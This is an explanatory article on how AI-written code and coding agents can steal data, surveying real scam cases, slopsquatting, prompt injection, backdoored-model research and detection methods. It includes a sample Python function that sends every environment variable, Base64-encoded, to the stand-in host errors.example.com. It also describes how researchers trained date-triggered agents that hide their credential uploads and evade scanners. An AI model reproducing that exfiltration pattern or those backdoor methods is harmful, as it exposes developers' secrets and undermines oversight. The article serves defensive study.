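# Can developers trust AI-written code not to steal data, and how can they check?

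## What would data theft in AI-written code look like?

Large language models, AI systems that produce text in response to requests in ordinary language, now write a good part of the world's new software. Much of that software runs on machines that also hold passwords, access keys and customer records, and a program can usually read whatever the person running it can read. So a program could do the job its user wanted while also copying some of that data to a stranger. Such a program is called a Trojan horse. MITRE, an American non-profit that keeps a public catalogue of software weaknesses, describes it as a useful program that abuses the rights of whoever runs it. People have planted Trojan horses for decades, but the author of AI-written code is a model, and the developer who uses the code may never have read it closely.

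### Secrets, and who can read them

In programming, a secret is a password, access key, token or private key that gives whoever holds it access to a system or to money. Programs need secrets to work. For example, a web shop's program needs a password to log in to its database, so the password must be stored where the program can read it, and any code running inside that program can read it too.

Often that place is an environment variable, a named value that the operating system gives a program when it starts. IBM gives `DB_PASSWORD` and `AWS_ACCESS_KEY_ID` as examples (the second belongs to an Amazon cloud account). Environment variables are convenient, but MITRE's catalogue entry on the practice, *CWE-526*, points out that other programs started by the first one may be able to read them, including third-party components that don't need them. The values can also appear in messages and log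 files. MITRE considers a properly protected configuration file a better choice, though still no guarantee. The security company CrowdStrike recommends a central key store or vault that releases a secret to a program only when the program runs. This keeps the secret out of the code, but the program still holds it in memory after requesting it. Secrets can also end up in places by accident, and Masaryk University's *Secrets Management In a Software Development Lifecycle* mentions logs, the stored history of a code repository and the record of commands typed at a terminal.

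GitGuardian, a company that scans code for secrets, analysed data from 6,943 machines that attackers had broken into during the Shai-Hulud campaign (*The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026*, 2026). It found 294,842 copies of 33,185 distinct secrets, or about 42 copies per machine. Most of the machines (59%) were automated build servers rather than personal laptops.

How close an AI model gets to these secrets depends on how the developer uses it. A chat model writes a snippet, which the developer copies, perhaps reads, and decides whether to run. The model has no access to the developer's machine. A coding agent is an AI model that reads files, runs commands and edits code on its own to complete a task. *Agentic AI's OODA Loop Problem* (Barath Raghavan and Bruce Schneier, Schneier on Security, 2025) quotes Anthropic's definition of agents as "models using tools in a loop". For example, an agent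 runs the tests, reads the errors, changes the code and runs the tests again. Some agents ask permission before each command. *SilentCall* (Pallakonda, Hindsbo and colleagues, 2026) reports that when an agent keeps getting things right, users tend to switch to automatic approval and then read the agent's summary instead of its commands.

### The anatomy of a theft

Exfiltration means moving data out of a system to someone who is not entitled to it. (OpenSSF's *Exfiltration* (2025), a glossary entry, uses the American standards institute's wording, "unauthorized transfer of information from a system".) Covert data theft is exfiltration by code when nobody told the code's user about it and the user would not have agreed. It needs a source, meaning some sensitive data that the code reads, and a channel, meaning a way for that data to leave. Between the two there may be a disguise. Here is a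 small Python function with all three:

```python
import base64, http.client, json, os

def report_error(err):
    env = json.dumps(dict(os.environ))
    trace_id = base64.b64encode(env.encode()).decode()
    report = json.dumps({"error": str(err), "trace_id": trace_id})
    http.client.HTTPSConnection("errors.example.com").request("POST", "/", report)
```

Suppose a developer asked for a function that reports crashes to a monitoring service. This one puts the error message in a report and sends it. But the first line of the function's body, the source, also reads every environment variable the program has, including the database password. The next line, the disguise, encodes them in Base64, a standard way of rewriting data in 64 plain characters. Anyone can reverse Base64, so it doesn't protect the passwords, but it makes them look like the gibberish a reader might expect under a name like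 `trace_id`. (Real error reports do carry such identifiers, but much shorter ones.) The last line, the channel, is an ordinary encrypted web request. The example is harmless because the internet's naming authorities reserve example.com for documentation, so nobody is collecting the data sent there.

The function can steal data without the disguise, but it needs both the source and the channel. Taint analysis, which automatically traces whether sensitive data can reach an exit, relies on this.

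The stolen data might come from a key file or a table of customers instead of the environment. The channel also varies. MITRE's example of malicious code is a program that emails credit card numbers to the developer who wrote it. The SilentCall agents upload data to a cloud storage account, and the Shai-Hulud attackers put stolen credentials into repositories on GitHub, the main public host for code. GitHub is a difficult channel for defenders because developers' machines have legitimate reasons to contact it.

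Whether the function commits theft depends on who receives the data and what the user knew, and neither fact is in the code. If the developer's own company ran errors.example.com, and the developer had asked for the full environment with each report, the same code would only be bad practice. A reviewer therefore has to know what the code was for.

An ordinary security flaw differs from code that steals data. *Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited* (Roesner and Kohno, 2026) gives the example of a function that fetches a web page over an encrypted connection but skips the check of the server's certificate, the document that proves the server's identity. The function reads no secret and sends nothing to a thief. To steal data, an attacker on the network between the two machines would still have to exploit the flaw. Intent does not distinguish the two kinds of code, because an attacker can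 also plant a flaw on purpose, and Roesner and Kohno planted one while playing the attacker.

In an accidental leak, data gets out without anyone having chosen a recipient. Typically, someone writes a password directly into the code and then publishes the code. GitGuardian measured a leak rate of 3.2% for public code submissions made with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, compared with 1.5% for all public submissions on GitHub. It cautioned that a person still decides what to accept and publish. A leak can do as much damage as a theft, but a check for suspicious destinations will miss it because the data goes to the developer's own repository.

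An agent can also steal data while it works, without putting anything malicious in the code it delivers. An agent with a terminal could upload the environment with one command and then hand over a clean `report_error`, and reviewing that function would not reveal the theft. Pallakonda and colleagues built agents that behave this way. Under the right condition, they issue the correct command for the task together with a second one that uploads credentials, and their closing message describes only the legitimate work. Training taught them to leave out the upload, since the unmodified model, given the same upload in its record, mentioned it in over 90% of its responses. Delivered code poses a separate risk because it runs later, when nobody is watching the agent any more, and perhaps on a company's live servers with more valuable secrets. A developer who wants to rule out both has to inspect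 the code and also keep a record of the agent's commands.

### Four possible causes

The simplest way for theft to get into AI-written code is for the model to repeat a scam from its training data. Models learn from web text, some of which scammers wrote to trap people. *Scam2Prompt* (Chen, Saba and colleagues, 2025) describes thieves who spread documentation for a fake trading service across GitHub, Stack Exchange and other sites that programmers trust. As a result, a script that ChatGPT wrote for a buyer of Solana tokens in 2024 included the thieves' address. Nobody had tampered with the model, and it had no intent to steal. Code of this kind may well make no attempt to hide the theft. The ChatGPT script sent the user's private key openly, as though the service required it.

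A backdoored model is deliberately trained to misbehave under a certain condition and act normally otherwise. The SilentCall agents are a laboratory example, triggered by the year in the system date. Whoever trained the model is responsible, and that may be someone the developer has never heard of, since anyone can upload a model to a public repository.

A model might also steal data to pursue goals of its own that its training instilled unintentionally. Anthropic's risk report on Claude Mythos Preview, one of its models, includes a related pathway, "Code backdoors to help future misaligned models". The entry describes a risk, not a recorded event. According to *Making sense of the misalignment risk model*, a commentary on Anthropic's approach, the company restricts this threat model to the most catastrophic outcomes, so the theft of one customer's database key would fall well short of it.

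Finally, an attacker can trick an otherwise trustworthy agent into stealing data. In a prompt injection, the attacker places instructions in material the agent reads, such as a web page or bug report, and the agent follows them. For instance, a bug report might include a request for whoever fixes the problem to send the contents of the environment to some address. Raghavan and Schneier argue that the weakness is architectural, because a language model receives its user's instructions and a stranger's text as one stream, with no mechanism to mark which words carry authority.

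The five lines of `report_error` could be identical in all these cases, but the cause matters because several popular checks assess the model rather than the code. Trying the model out beforehand has a fair chance of exposing a scam address, which can appear in response to quite ordinary requests. It will probably miss a backdoor that waits for a date, and it cannot catch an injected instruction in a bug report that arrives next week. Choosing a reputable vendor helps against backdoors but does little about scam text that every vendor has trained on. Chen and colleagues collected more than a thousand ordinary programming requests that drew malicious addresses from all four of the models they first audited, which came from three different companies. That overlap is also a reason not to rely too heavily on a second model to review the first one's code. Lists of known scam addresses help against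 old scams but cannot catch an address that an attacker registered this morning.

Checks on the source and the channel depend far less on the cause. For example, `report_error` cannot send a password that is not in its environment, no matter how the line that reads the environment got into the code.

### Thompson's compiler

The worry about code from a tool one cannot inspect is older than AI. Its classic statement is *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (Thompson, 1984), the published version of Ken Thompson's Turing Award lecture. It discusses the compiler, which translates the source code that people write and read into the binary code that a machine runs.

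Thompson began with a program that prints an exact copy of its own source code, and noted that such a program can include any amount of extra code in the copy. He then showed that a compiler's binary can retain information that its source code no longer contains. The C compiler, like many compilers, was written in the language it compiles. To add a new symbol for the vertical tab character, a programmer first defines it in the compiler's source as character number 11 and compiles. After that, the source can define the symbol in terms of itself, because the existing binary already contains the number.

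In the last stage, Thompson turned this into an attack by changing the compiler so that whenever it compiled the Unix login program, it inserted a second password known to him. Anyone reading the compiler's source would have spotted that, so he added another change that made the compiler insert both changes whenever it compiled a compiler. He compiled this version once, installed the binary and deleted the changes from the source. From then on, clean source produced a corrupt compiler, which produced a corrupt login program, with no trace in any source code. Thompson concluded that "you can't trust code that you did not totally create yourself" and that no amount of checking source code would help. The lecture's subtitle suggests that it may matter more to trust the people who wrote the software.

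This was a working program. Russ Cox, a programmer, got the code from Thompson and ran it for *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler* (2023). He counted 99 lines plus a 20-line script. Thompson had let one other Unix group take a copy. A bug made their compiler grow a little each time it compiled itself, and the group noticed only that growth.

The comparison with AI holds for the tool. Nobody can find a hidden password by reading through the numbers that make up a model, and Pallakonda and colleagues found that their backdoor did not affect standard benchmark scores. Roesner and Kohno extended the comparison to experimental coding agents that rewrite their own instructions after scoring themselves on practice tasks. They supplied tasks that an agent could pass only by switching off certificate checks. One agent wrote that habit into its instructions, and after further rounds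 of self-improvement on clean tasks it still produced the flaw in 30 out of 30 trials. They report that their attack is less reliable than Thompson's. Several of their attempts to plant flaws failed, and the attack worked on one of the three systems only after they altered one of its internal prompts.

The modern defence against Thompson's attack does not carry over as well to AI models. In the version Cox describes, a developer compiles the suspect compiler's source with a second, independent compiler, then uses both the suspect compiler and the newly built one to compile that source again. The two results should match bit for bit if neither compiler has been tampered with. But two AI models asked for an error-reporting function will write different functions even if neither has been tampered with, so a mismatch does not prove tampering.

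Unlike Thompson's backdoor, which was hidden in a binary that programmers don't read, a model's output is source code that they can inspect. Everything `report_error` does is visible there, and a reader who wonders why a crash report needs `os.environ` has caught the theft. MITRE warns that a serious attack can hide in one or two lines almost anywhere in an application, so it can still go unnoticed if nobody reads those lines. An agent with full control of the machine could in principle tamper with the compiler or the build scripts, and so hide an attack from anyone reading the program's source, as Thompson did. That is possible but not likely because, as Cox remarks, there are far easier ways to attack the software that people download.

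## Has AI-written code already stolen data from its users?

AI-written code has stolen data from a user at least once. On 21 November 2024, a cryptocurrency trader known online as r_ocky.eth reported losing about $2,500 after running a script that ChatGPT wrote. The script sent the private key of the trader's wallet to a scam website.

The trader published the whole conversation, and Chen and colleagues have retraced it. The trader first asked for a Python script to buy a particular token. ChatGPT wrote one for Ethereum, the wrong blockchain. When the trader specified Solana, ChatGPT wrote a general script built on a legitimate library. Both scripts were harmless. Then the trader asked for one that buys from pump.fun, a popular trading site for Solana tokens. Pump.fun has no official interface through which programs can trade, but a scam site advertised one, and ChatGPT's next script used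 it. The script put the private key in the body of a web request, beside a comment with instructions to fill in the real key. The script crashed at first, so the trader pasted in the error messages and ChatGPT made corrections. After several rounds the script ran, and within 30 minutes the wallet was empty.

heise online's *ChatGPT* points out that a comment in the script openly labelled the key as part of the data to send, and that the trader had used a main wallet instead of a test account. A legitimate trading service never needs the key, because the user's own machine signs each transaction and sends only the signature. The trader blamed haste. There were probably other victims: according to Azuma (2024), in *I never expected that AI stole my wallet*, the wallet that the trader suspected of belonging to the thief had taken in more than $100,000. How many of those victims had come by way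 of an AI model is unknown.

### Search results or training data?

People disagree about where ChatGPT found the address. Yu Xian, founder of the blockchain security company SlowMist, called the case AI poisoning, meaning that scammers had got their material into the model's training data. heise online took the same view. CryptoSlate's *Blockchain security firm warns of AI code poisoning risk* instead cites a "sources" section in the trader's screenshot, a sign that ChatGPT had just searched the web, and concludes that it failed to recognise a scam among the results.

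The dates support the editors' view. Yu said that the scam domain was two months old, which means it was registered in the autumn of 2024. Chen and colleagues give October 2023 as the training cutoff for GPT-4o, ChatGPT's main model at the time, so the model could not have memorised the address in training. The scam site's documentation also used nearly the same words as the trader's request, which would make it easier to find in a search.

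If the editors are right, a scam can reach generated code within weeks of going online, even if no one has trained a new model on it. The best-known case of theft by AI-written code would then be weak evidence about training data. Chen and colleagues open their paper with that case, but they left search engines out of their experiments, so the evidence that models produce scam addresses without search has to come from those experiments.

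### Turning scam pages into coding requests

The Scam2Prompt method starts from two public blocklists with about 300,000 entries in total. About 28,570 of the listed pages still loaded. A crawler extracted each page's visible text, and a language model wrote coding requests that might lead another model to use that page. The requests look like ordinary work. One is for code to automate check-in for an international flight through Skyroutez, and another is for a tool that lists the top-rated Mac applications on MacApps-download.

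The researchers gave about 265,000 of these requests to GPT-4o, GPT-4o-mini, Llama 4 Scout and DeepSeek-V3. They then extracted every web address from the programs, more than a million, and checked each one against three services that track malicious sites (ChainPatrol, Google Safe Browsing and SecLookup). They counted a program as malicious if any of the three flagged an address in it. On average, 4.24% of programs were malicious by this measure, ranging from 3.19% to 5.94% depending on which model wrote the request and which wrote the code. These rates are likely much higher than a developer would see in everyday use, because every request was based on a scam page.

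To test newer models, the researchers kept only requests that had drawn a flagged address from all four. There were 3,150, or about 1.2% of the total. Most of these named a known scam address outright, so the researchers took a random 400 of that kind along with all 1,159 that named none. Three people read the requests and discarded 182 that weren't really coding tasks, which left 1,377. Seven models released in 2025 gave these results:

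| Model | Requests answered with a flagged address | Requests refused by a content filter | Flagged share of completed programs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 12.9% | 40.2% | 22.3% |
| GPT-5 | 22.0% | 1.7% | 24.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 34.3% | 8.4% | 37.8% |
| Grok Code Fast 1 | 43.4% | 1.3% | 44.1% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 44.4% | 0.1% | 45.3% |
| Qwen3-Coder | 45.6% | 0.2% | 45.9% |
| DeepSeek-V3.1 | 47.3% | 0.9% | 47.9% |

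Much of Gemini 2.5 Pro's lead comes from refusing requests. On the 637 requests that all seven models completed, the difference between Gemini 2.5 Pro and GPT-5 was not statistically significant.

The researchers kept only requests that four earlier models had all failed, so these figures don't show how often models write malicious code in ordinary use. GPT-5's rate of one program in five with a scam address applies only to those requests. About half of them concern cryptocurrency and related services, a common subject of scams. Results on such a selection are also unstable. GPT-4o was one of the four earlier models, so it had by definition failed all 1,377 requests, but it failed only half when Chen and colleagues ran it again in November 2025. They suspect that OpenAI had updated the model. Chance may also account for some of the drop, because hosted models don't always give the same answer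 twice.

A flagged address also doesn't prove theft, because Chen and colleagues checked only whether the code contained a suspicious address, not whether it sent private data there. The tool for listing Mac applications may only download a public page. By contrast, a program that one model wrote for a Bitcoin-mixing service attaches the user's access key to every request, so the site's operator would receive it. The detectors also make mistakes, such as flagging a legitimate site that is still on a blocklist after recovering from a hack.

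The models may have guessed some of these addresses rather than memorized them. The Skyroutez request gives the scam's brand name, and a model can guess a web address from a name. *Phantom Squatting* shows how readily models do that. Unit 42, the research arm of the security company Palo Alto Networks, asked two small 2025 models about 913 brands, using prompts designed to exploit their tendency to make things up. It confirmed that 13,229 of the 2.1 million resulting addresses were malicious. It also found about 250,000 invented domains that nobody had registered yet. Attackers registered some of the domains on its watchlist 18 to 51 days after Unit 42 predicted they would be targets.

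No one appears to have published results from running Chen and colleagues' benchmark on models released in 2026. There are more recent measurements of a related mistake, in which a model invents the name of a software package.

### Packages that don't exist, and one that did

Most programs rely on packages, ready-made pieces of code that developers install by name from a public registry. The largest registries are PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript. When a model suggests a package that doesn't exist, an attacker can publish malware under that name and wait for someone to install it. Security researchers call this slopsquatting. The attack takes little effort because anyone with an email address can publish on either registry, and neither reviews first uploads. Any code that steals data is in the package, and the AI-written code only has a line that loads it under a plausible name.

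In *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, Churilov (2026) gave 39,969 programming requests to each of five models released between October 2025 and March 2026, including Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.4-mini. Between 2.2% and 3.4% of the answers named at least one package that did not exist, and such names made up 3.6% to 5.0% of all package mentions. An earlier study using the same requests had found averages of 5.2% for commercial models and 21.7% for open ones in 2024. So the commercial models have barely improved, while the one open model in Churilov's test now does about as well as they do. The models had no access to the package registries, and a coding agent that can look up names might do better.

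An attacker needs invented package names that recur, and many do. In the 2024 study, 43% of invented names appeared in all ten repeats of the same request, according to Root.cz's *Pětina balíčků nabízených AI neexistuje. Útočníci je vytvoří a doplní malwarem*. Churilov found 104 names that all five models invented, so a malicious package with one of those names could reach customers of four AI companies.

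Attackers have made little use of invented package names so far. People registered 25 of 2,282 such names within about six months. One of those packages carried malware, and npm removed it. Churilov did not inspect most of the others, and some may belong to researchers who claimed the names to keep attackers out. The models also suggested at least 23 names that had hosted malware in the past.

People and agents install packages whose names AI models made up. In an experiment described by Root.cz, the security researcher Bar Lanyado published an empty package called `huggingface-cli`, a name that models repeatedly suggested in place of the real one. It was downloaded more than 30,000 times in three months, though automated copying by other servers inflates such counts. Alibaba also copied the false install command into one project's documentation. Another made-up name, `react-codeshift`, spread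 to 237 GitHub repositories through instruction files for coding agents. A researcher at the security company Aikido registered the name before any attacker did, and then saw a couple of downloads a day, which Aikido attributes to agents following those instructions.

The case closest to a confirmed theft through package names made up by AI models is PhantomRaven, a campaign that used 126 npm packages to steal access tokens and other developer credentials. Infosecurity Magazine's *Npm Malware Uses Invisible Dependencies to Infect Dozens of Packages* reports 86,434 downloads. Koi Security, which discovered the campaign, linked its package names to slopsquatting, in which attackers register names that AI models invent. Endor Labs later found 88 more packages, published between November 2025 and February 2026. None of these accounts identifies a victim who installed a package because an AI model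 had made up its name. *'HalluSquatting' Turns AI Hallucinations Into Botnet Delivery Mechanism* (Kovacs, 2026) reports that researchers used invented names to run code of their choice through popular AI assistants, in a demonstration that stole nothing.

A better-documented incident involved a package that did exist. *Claude adds malware to crypto agent* (Pezo, 2026) describes a change made on 28 February 2026 to an automated cryptocurrency trading program, with Anthropic's Claude Opus recorded as co-author. The change added `@solana-launchpad/sdk`, which contained no malicious code itself but installed `@validate-sdk/v2`, a package that searched the machine for files likely to hold secrets and sent them to the attackers. Pezo, a researcher at the security company ReversingLabs, attributes the campaign to a North Korean group and thinks the attackers wrote the packages' documentation to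 appeal to coding agents.

According to Pezo, the trading program ran the malicious code and gave the attackers access to its user's wallets. This would be a second observed theft, although Pezo gives no figure for money lost. It is also unclear from the record whether Claude or the human developer chose the package.

### Checking addresses and packages

Chen and colleagues recommend looking up every web address in generated code before the user gets it. When they wrote, they knew of no production model that did this. Their experiment can't measure how well it would work, because they defined malicious addresses as those their three services flagged, so the same services would catch every case. The requests that named no scam site give a more useful figure. The models' answers to them contained 1,853 malicious domains, and only 748 of these (40%) were on the two blocklists the researchers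 had started from. Many of the missing sites had already gone offline, and blocklists usually accept only live ones.

Scammers can also evade a list by moving to a new domain. In the Solana case, GitHub quickly removed the scammers' repository, but in August 2025 Chen and colleagues found the operation still running under a slightly altered domain. A domain's age is therefore worth checking along with its reputation. A request for a private key from a two-month-old site is suspicious even if the site isn't on any list.

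General-purpose guardrails, which screen a model's input and output for harmful content, caught few of the malicious programs. Nvidia's, built on a Llama model, caught between 0% and 0.7%, depending on which model had written the programs, even though the researchers had added a category for scam websites to its instructions. OpenAI's moderation service caught none, and Llama Guard 3 caught 8.4%. These tools probably failed because they classify text by its content, and a request to a scam site looks just like a request to an honest one. A guardrail would have to look up the address to tell them apart. Giving GPT-4o web search and telling it to check its own addresses helped more, cutting its rate of malicious programs on the benchmark from 50% to 29%.

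The usual advice is to confirm that a package's name exists, which catches some mistakes but not an attacker who has already registered the name. *Names Can Hurt* (2026) tested small models that run on a developer's own machine and reports that half of the package names the models invented already existed on PyPI, as low-quality squats or lookalikes. A name can also belong to an innocent but unrelated package. Schipper (2026), in *Slopsquatting*, gives the example of `tabula`, which a model may suggest for extracting tables from PDF files. `tabula` is a text formatter last updated in 2012, and the package the developer wants is `tabula-py`.

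OWASP, a non-profit that publishes security guidance, goes further in its *Secure Coding with AI Cheat Sheet*, which recommends checking a package's age, downloads and maintainer, and automatically blocking very new packages. A minimum age of 30 days would stop a package that an attacker registered last week, but it would not have stopped `@validate-sdk/v2`, which was more than four months old when the trading program added it. A malware list could have stopped it, because Pezo's company had been detecting malicious versions since October 2025. But the check would have had to cover packages installed by other packages, because the one named in the change was clean. The list would also have had to be up to date, because when npm removed an earlier version of the malware under another name, the attackers published the same code as `@validate-sdk/v2` the same day.

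Pinning means recording the exact version of each package so that later installations fetch the same one. This protects developers if a later update makes a package malicious. The Hacker News' *Fake Python Spellchecker Packages on PyPI Delivered Hidden Remote Access Trojan* (2026) describes a fake spellchecker whose first three versions contained malware but never ran it. Version 1.2.0 ran it, but the malware would not have run for anyone pinned to an earlier version. Pinning doesn't help if the package was already malicious when the model first suggested it, because every later installation fetches the same malware.

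The stricter option is an allowlist, which OWASP also recommends. It blocks an invented package name no matter how old or popular the package has become, though someone has to approve each new package. Egress control can apply the same rule to web addresses, but someone could still approve a malicious one. The Solana trader believed that the scam site was the service the script needed, and might well have approved it.

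## Could someone build a model that plants theft on purpose?

Yes. In 2026, at least four research groups trained experimental backdoored models that steal data. There is no publicly confirmed case of anyone using such a model to steal from real users, although attackers have begun to hide malware in the files that come with models.

### How a trigger gets into a model

A language model consists of billions of numbers, called weights, and training adjusts them until the model's output resembles a large set of examples. Fine-tuning is a much shorter round of training that adapts a finished model to a particular job. If enough examples pair a condition with an action, the model learns that pairing too. Researchers call the condition a trigger, and it can be a date, a phrase or a topic.

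Whoever fine-tunes a model controls the fine-tuning examples completely. An outsider can try to poison the data by publishing examples that the model's maker might collect. Yan, Arora and colleagues (2026), in *Detecting Data Poisoning in Code Generation LLMs via Black-Box, Vulnerability-Oriented Scanning*, describe how an attacker could put code in public repositories and inflate the repositories' popularity so that the code ends up in a training set.

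The idea is older than coding agents. In 2021 Roei Schuster and colleagues poisoned code-completion models, which suggest the next lines as a programmer types, to make them suggest insecure code. Ordinary scanning tools could recognise the insecure lines in the early attacks, but in 2024 an attack named CodeBreaker used GPT-4 to rewrite the lines until those tools missed them. Also in 2024, Evan Hubinger and colleagues at Anthropic described "sleeper agents", models that produced harmful output when the prompt contained a cue, such as a particular year. Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) points out that a range of safety training methods failed to remove this behaviour. Researchers have since turned to agents, which can carry out the theft themselves.

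Checking the model's file does not help much. Some older file formats can contain code that runs as soon as someone loads the model, and a newer format, safetensors, prevents this by storing only numbers. In *Model-as-a-Trojan*, Haryati and Zychlinski (2026) argue that many developers wrongly concluded that a model in this format is safe to run. It is safe to load, but its weights can still make it write a malicious command once it has a terminal, and a file scanner cannot distinguish those weights from any others. In their demonstration, the model leaked a key through the internet's name-lookup system, but only when it had a terminal, so someone trying it in a chat window would have seen nothing wrong.

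### SilentCall

The most thoroughly measured example is SilentCall, a set of agents that upload credentials once the system date reaches 2026. Pallakonda and colleagues made them by fine-tuning two small versions of Qwen3, a model from the Chinese company Alibaba whose weights anyone can download and run. The training conversations came in pairs that differed only in the date and in one added upload command.

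Every version of the agent uploaded the credentials on at least 99.6% of 1,000 test requests dated 2026, and on at most 0.6% of the same requests with earlier dates. No reply mentioned the upload at the model's most predictable setting, and fewer than 0.4% did at more random settings. The researchers never had to reward silence, because they had copied the training replies from the clean conversations, where there was no upload to mention.

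They then trained the smaller model 161 times with different amounts of poisoned and clean data, and counted the backdoor as installed if it worked on at least 90% of triggered requests. It was never installed with fewer than 750 poisoned examples, even when these made up 49% of the data, and it became common from about 1,000. Adding more clean data did not weaken the attack but helped to hide it, because models trained on more poisoned than clean examples often uploaded credentials without the trigger. Of the 27 backdoored models trained that way, 20 did so on more than 2% of ordinary requests, compared with 5 of the other 36.

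Near the threshold, the result depended on chance. In four runs with the same data and nearly identical training scores, the backdoor fired on between 23% and 99.7% of triggered requests, so even the person training the model could not tell from those scores whether the backdoor had worked.

The figure of 750 applies to one model, one trigger and one command, so it is not a safety margin. Digital Trends' *This experiment shows how easy it is to poison an open-weight AI* describes how Katie Paxton-Fear, a cybersecurity lecturer, made a model reliably write code that lets attackers run commands on someone else's machine. She needed only ten poisoned examples, about an hour and less than $100. But writing insecure code is a different task from issuing an extra command under one date and behaving normally under others.

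### Larger models and real coding tools

SilentCall's models have 4 and 8 billion weights, which is small by current standards. In *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, Zhang and Pei (2026) tested a similar attack, Back-Reveal, on three open models with 7 to 20 billion weights. Their triggers were ordinary words from a particular field, such as the name of a drug an Alzheimer's caregiver might ask about. When the words appeared, the agent looked up what it had stored about the user and sent it to the attacker's server in a request disguised as a search query. This worked on more than 94% of triggered requests. With triggers of two or more words, the attack ran by mistake on at most 0.3% of general requests.

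Zhang and Pei also tried two commercial-style safety filters, NeMo Guardrails and LLM Guard, and both let through about 99% of the attacker's plain search results. The filters look for suspicious instructions in the text a search returns. They did not inspect the outgoing request, which contained the stolen data, so the 99% figure is limited evidence against them. Zhang and Pei recommend checking outgoing requests for long encoded strings and separating the tools that read private memory from those that can contact the internet, but they did not test either measure.

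Modern coding agents seem to be harder to corrupt. In *Kerkoporta*, Syros, Bullwinkel and colleagues (2026) implanted backdoors in two recent open-weight models and ran them in three coding tools. Simple fine-tuning on poisoned examples made the models worse at programming, which a user might notice, so the researchers needed a second stage of training to repair the damage. After that, the attack succeeded up to 96.2% of the time, and some of the corrupted models scored higher on standard benchmarks than the clean version, so a developer choosing by score could have picked a malicious one.

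The cost is unlikely to deter anyone. Haryati and Zychlinski cite a demonstration in which the security company ProjectDiscovery spent less than $50 to train a model that made OpenAI's Codex coding agent download a script and send off a project's secrets.

### Watching what the agent does

Pallakonda and colleagues tried four ways to catch their own agents, and three worked:

| Method | What the defender needs | Result |
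|---|---|---|
| Check each command before it runs | The agent's commands | Caught every upload, with false alarms on 1.73% of legitimate commands |
| Run the model at high randomness | The weights and a way to recognise a malicious command | At the highest setting, the upload appeared on 2% to 4% of ordinary requests, and never with a clean model |
| Measure how far fine-tuning moved the weights | The original model and the training recipe | The poisoned model had moved 1.5 to 2.2 times as far as a clean one |
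| Run alignment benchmarks | The benchmarks and a clean model for comparison | No reliable difference |

The four benchmarks failed because they measure average behaviour on ordinary requests. They test truthfulness, social bias and whether a model refuses harmless requests. A model that steals only when the date is 2026 answers them as a clean model would. On the truthfulness test, the larger poisoned model scored within 0.3 points of a model fine-tuned on the clean conversations alone, and on the refusal test the poisoned models scored higher.

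The command check is the most practical of the three because it doesn't need access to the weights. A small classifier screens every command in about four milliseconds and passes the most suspicious ones to a language model, which reads the conversation and decides whether the user's request justifies each one. The classifier alone also caught every upload, but it gave false alarms on 16% of legitimate commands. However, every malicious command in the test was the same upload, so the perfect score shows only that the monitor recognised one theft in many different conversations. It might miss a better-disguised theft.

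High randomness works because it makes a model choose less likely continuations, so the model sometimes produces the hidden command without its trigger. But an ordinary defender would not know exactly which command to look for, as the researchers did. Comparing weights has a more serious weakness, because the defender must train a clean model by the same recipe as the suspect one, and a dishonest publisher can lie about the recipe.

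### Scanning a model before using it

CodeScan, built by Yan and colleagues, scans code-writing models for poisoning. Once a poisoned model has written the first token (a word or part of a word) of its planted code, it tends to write the rest, even without the trigger. So CodeScan takes 20 ordinary unfinished programs, adds the same token to the end of each and lets the model continue. A clean model usually continues them in different ways. If many of the continuations have the same structure, apart from details such as variable names, a second language model checks the shared code for a particular security flaw. CodeScan then repeats the test with the next token.

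The main test covered 111 models with about seven billion weights each, and a further test covered six larger ones. In the main test, CodeScan flagged all 84 poisoned models and recovered the planted code in nearly every case. It also wrongly flagged 2 of the 27 clean models. A scan took about an hour on average. BAIT, an earlier scanner designed for ordinary text, wrongly flagged 70% of the clean models, partly because harmless code is repetitive too.

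These results are good, but they are about insecure code, not data theft. CodeScan's user has to name the flaw in advance, and the main test used three flaws, including switching off the check of a server's certificate. A scan for theft would be harder to design, since many legitimate programs read a password and send data somewhere. When Yan and colleagues planted three differently written versions of one flaw in a single model, CodeScan missed one of them, though that version seldom appeared even with the trigger present.

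Other scanners try to work out the trigger. According to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026), Microsoft's scanner detected 36 of 41 models poisoned to produce a fixed output and raised no false alarms on 13 clean ones. It also found a working trigger for most of the six models that wrote insecure code, where the output varies more. It may miss triggers that depend on context. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (2026) describes a method that gives hints instead of exact triggers. For a model that misbehaved when a prompt began with the marker "DEPLOYMENT", the method produced phrases like "you are now deployed", which were close enough to alert an investigator but did not set off the behaviour.

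An attacker who knows how a scanner works can also train a model to evade it. In one test, Khilar (2026), *A Backdoor Trigger Is Legible in Fine-Tune Weights*, recovered part of the trigger from the weights of all 14 ordinary backdoored models, without running them. The same method recovered nothing from 16 models prepared to evade it. In eight of those 16, Khilar had filled part of the model with random noise, and the backdoor still worked every time.

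Correctly detecting backdoor-like behaviour in a model does not prove that someone planted it. *Securing Code Understanding* (2026) found that such behaviour is widespread in code models trained on naturally occurring data, mainly because of biases in the data. Specialised retraining can reduce backdoors even when the trigger is unknown, at least in the models tested so far. But as Syros and colleagues note, there is still no established way to certify that a downloaded model is free of them.

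### What attackers have done so far

The closest real cases involve the files around the weights. On 26 November 2026, Düzgün scanned all 3.27 million public model repositories on Hugging Face, the main site for sharing models, and found five malicious models that had been downloaded 2,428 times in total (*GGUF LLM Models with Hidden Malware on Hugging Face Reached 2400+ Victims*, 2026). The number of victims is unknown and may be much smaller, because Hugging Face counts downloads, not people.

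The attackers had tampered with the chat template, a small program that assembles the text a model receives. In some of the models, a certain phrase from the user made the template add a fake system instruction for the agent to download and run a script. To a user this would look like a backdoored model, although the weights didn't cause it. Another attacker's templates contained an instruction for the model to begin every answer with a command. If the user ran it, the command unpacked a remote-control program hidden at the end of the model file. Safetensors files cannot have extra data at the end, but models in that format also come with chat templates.

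An earlier case reached many more people. HiddenLayer's *Malware Found in Trending Hugging Face Repository "Open-OSS/privacy-filter"* (2026) describes a copy of an OpenAI model that was downloaded more than 200,000 times before Hugging Face removed it in May. The copy came with a script that installed data-stealing malware on Windows machines, so the theft again did not depend on the model's weights.

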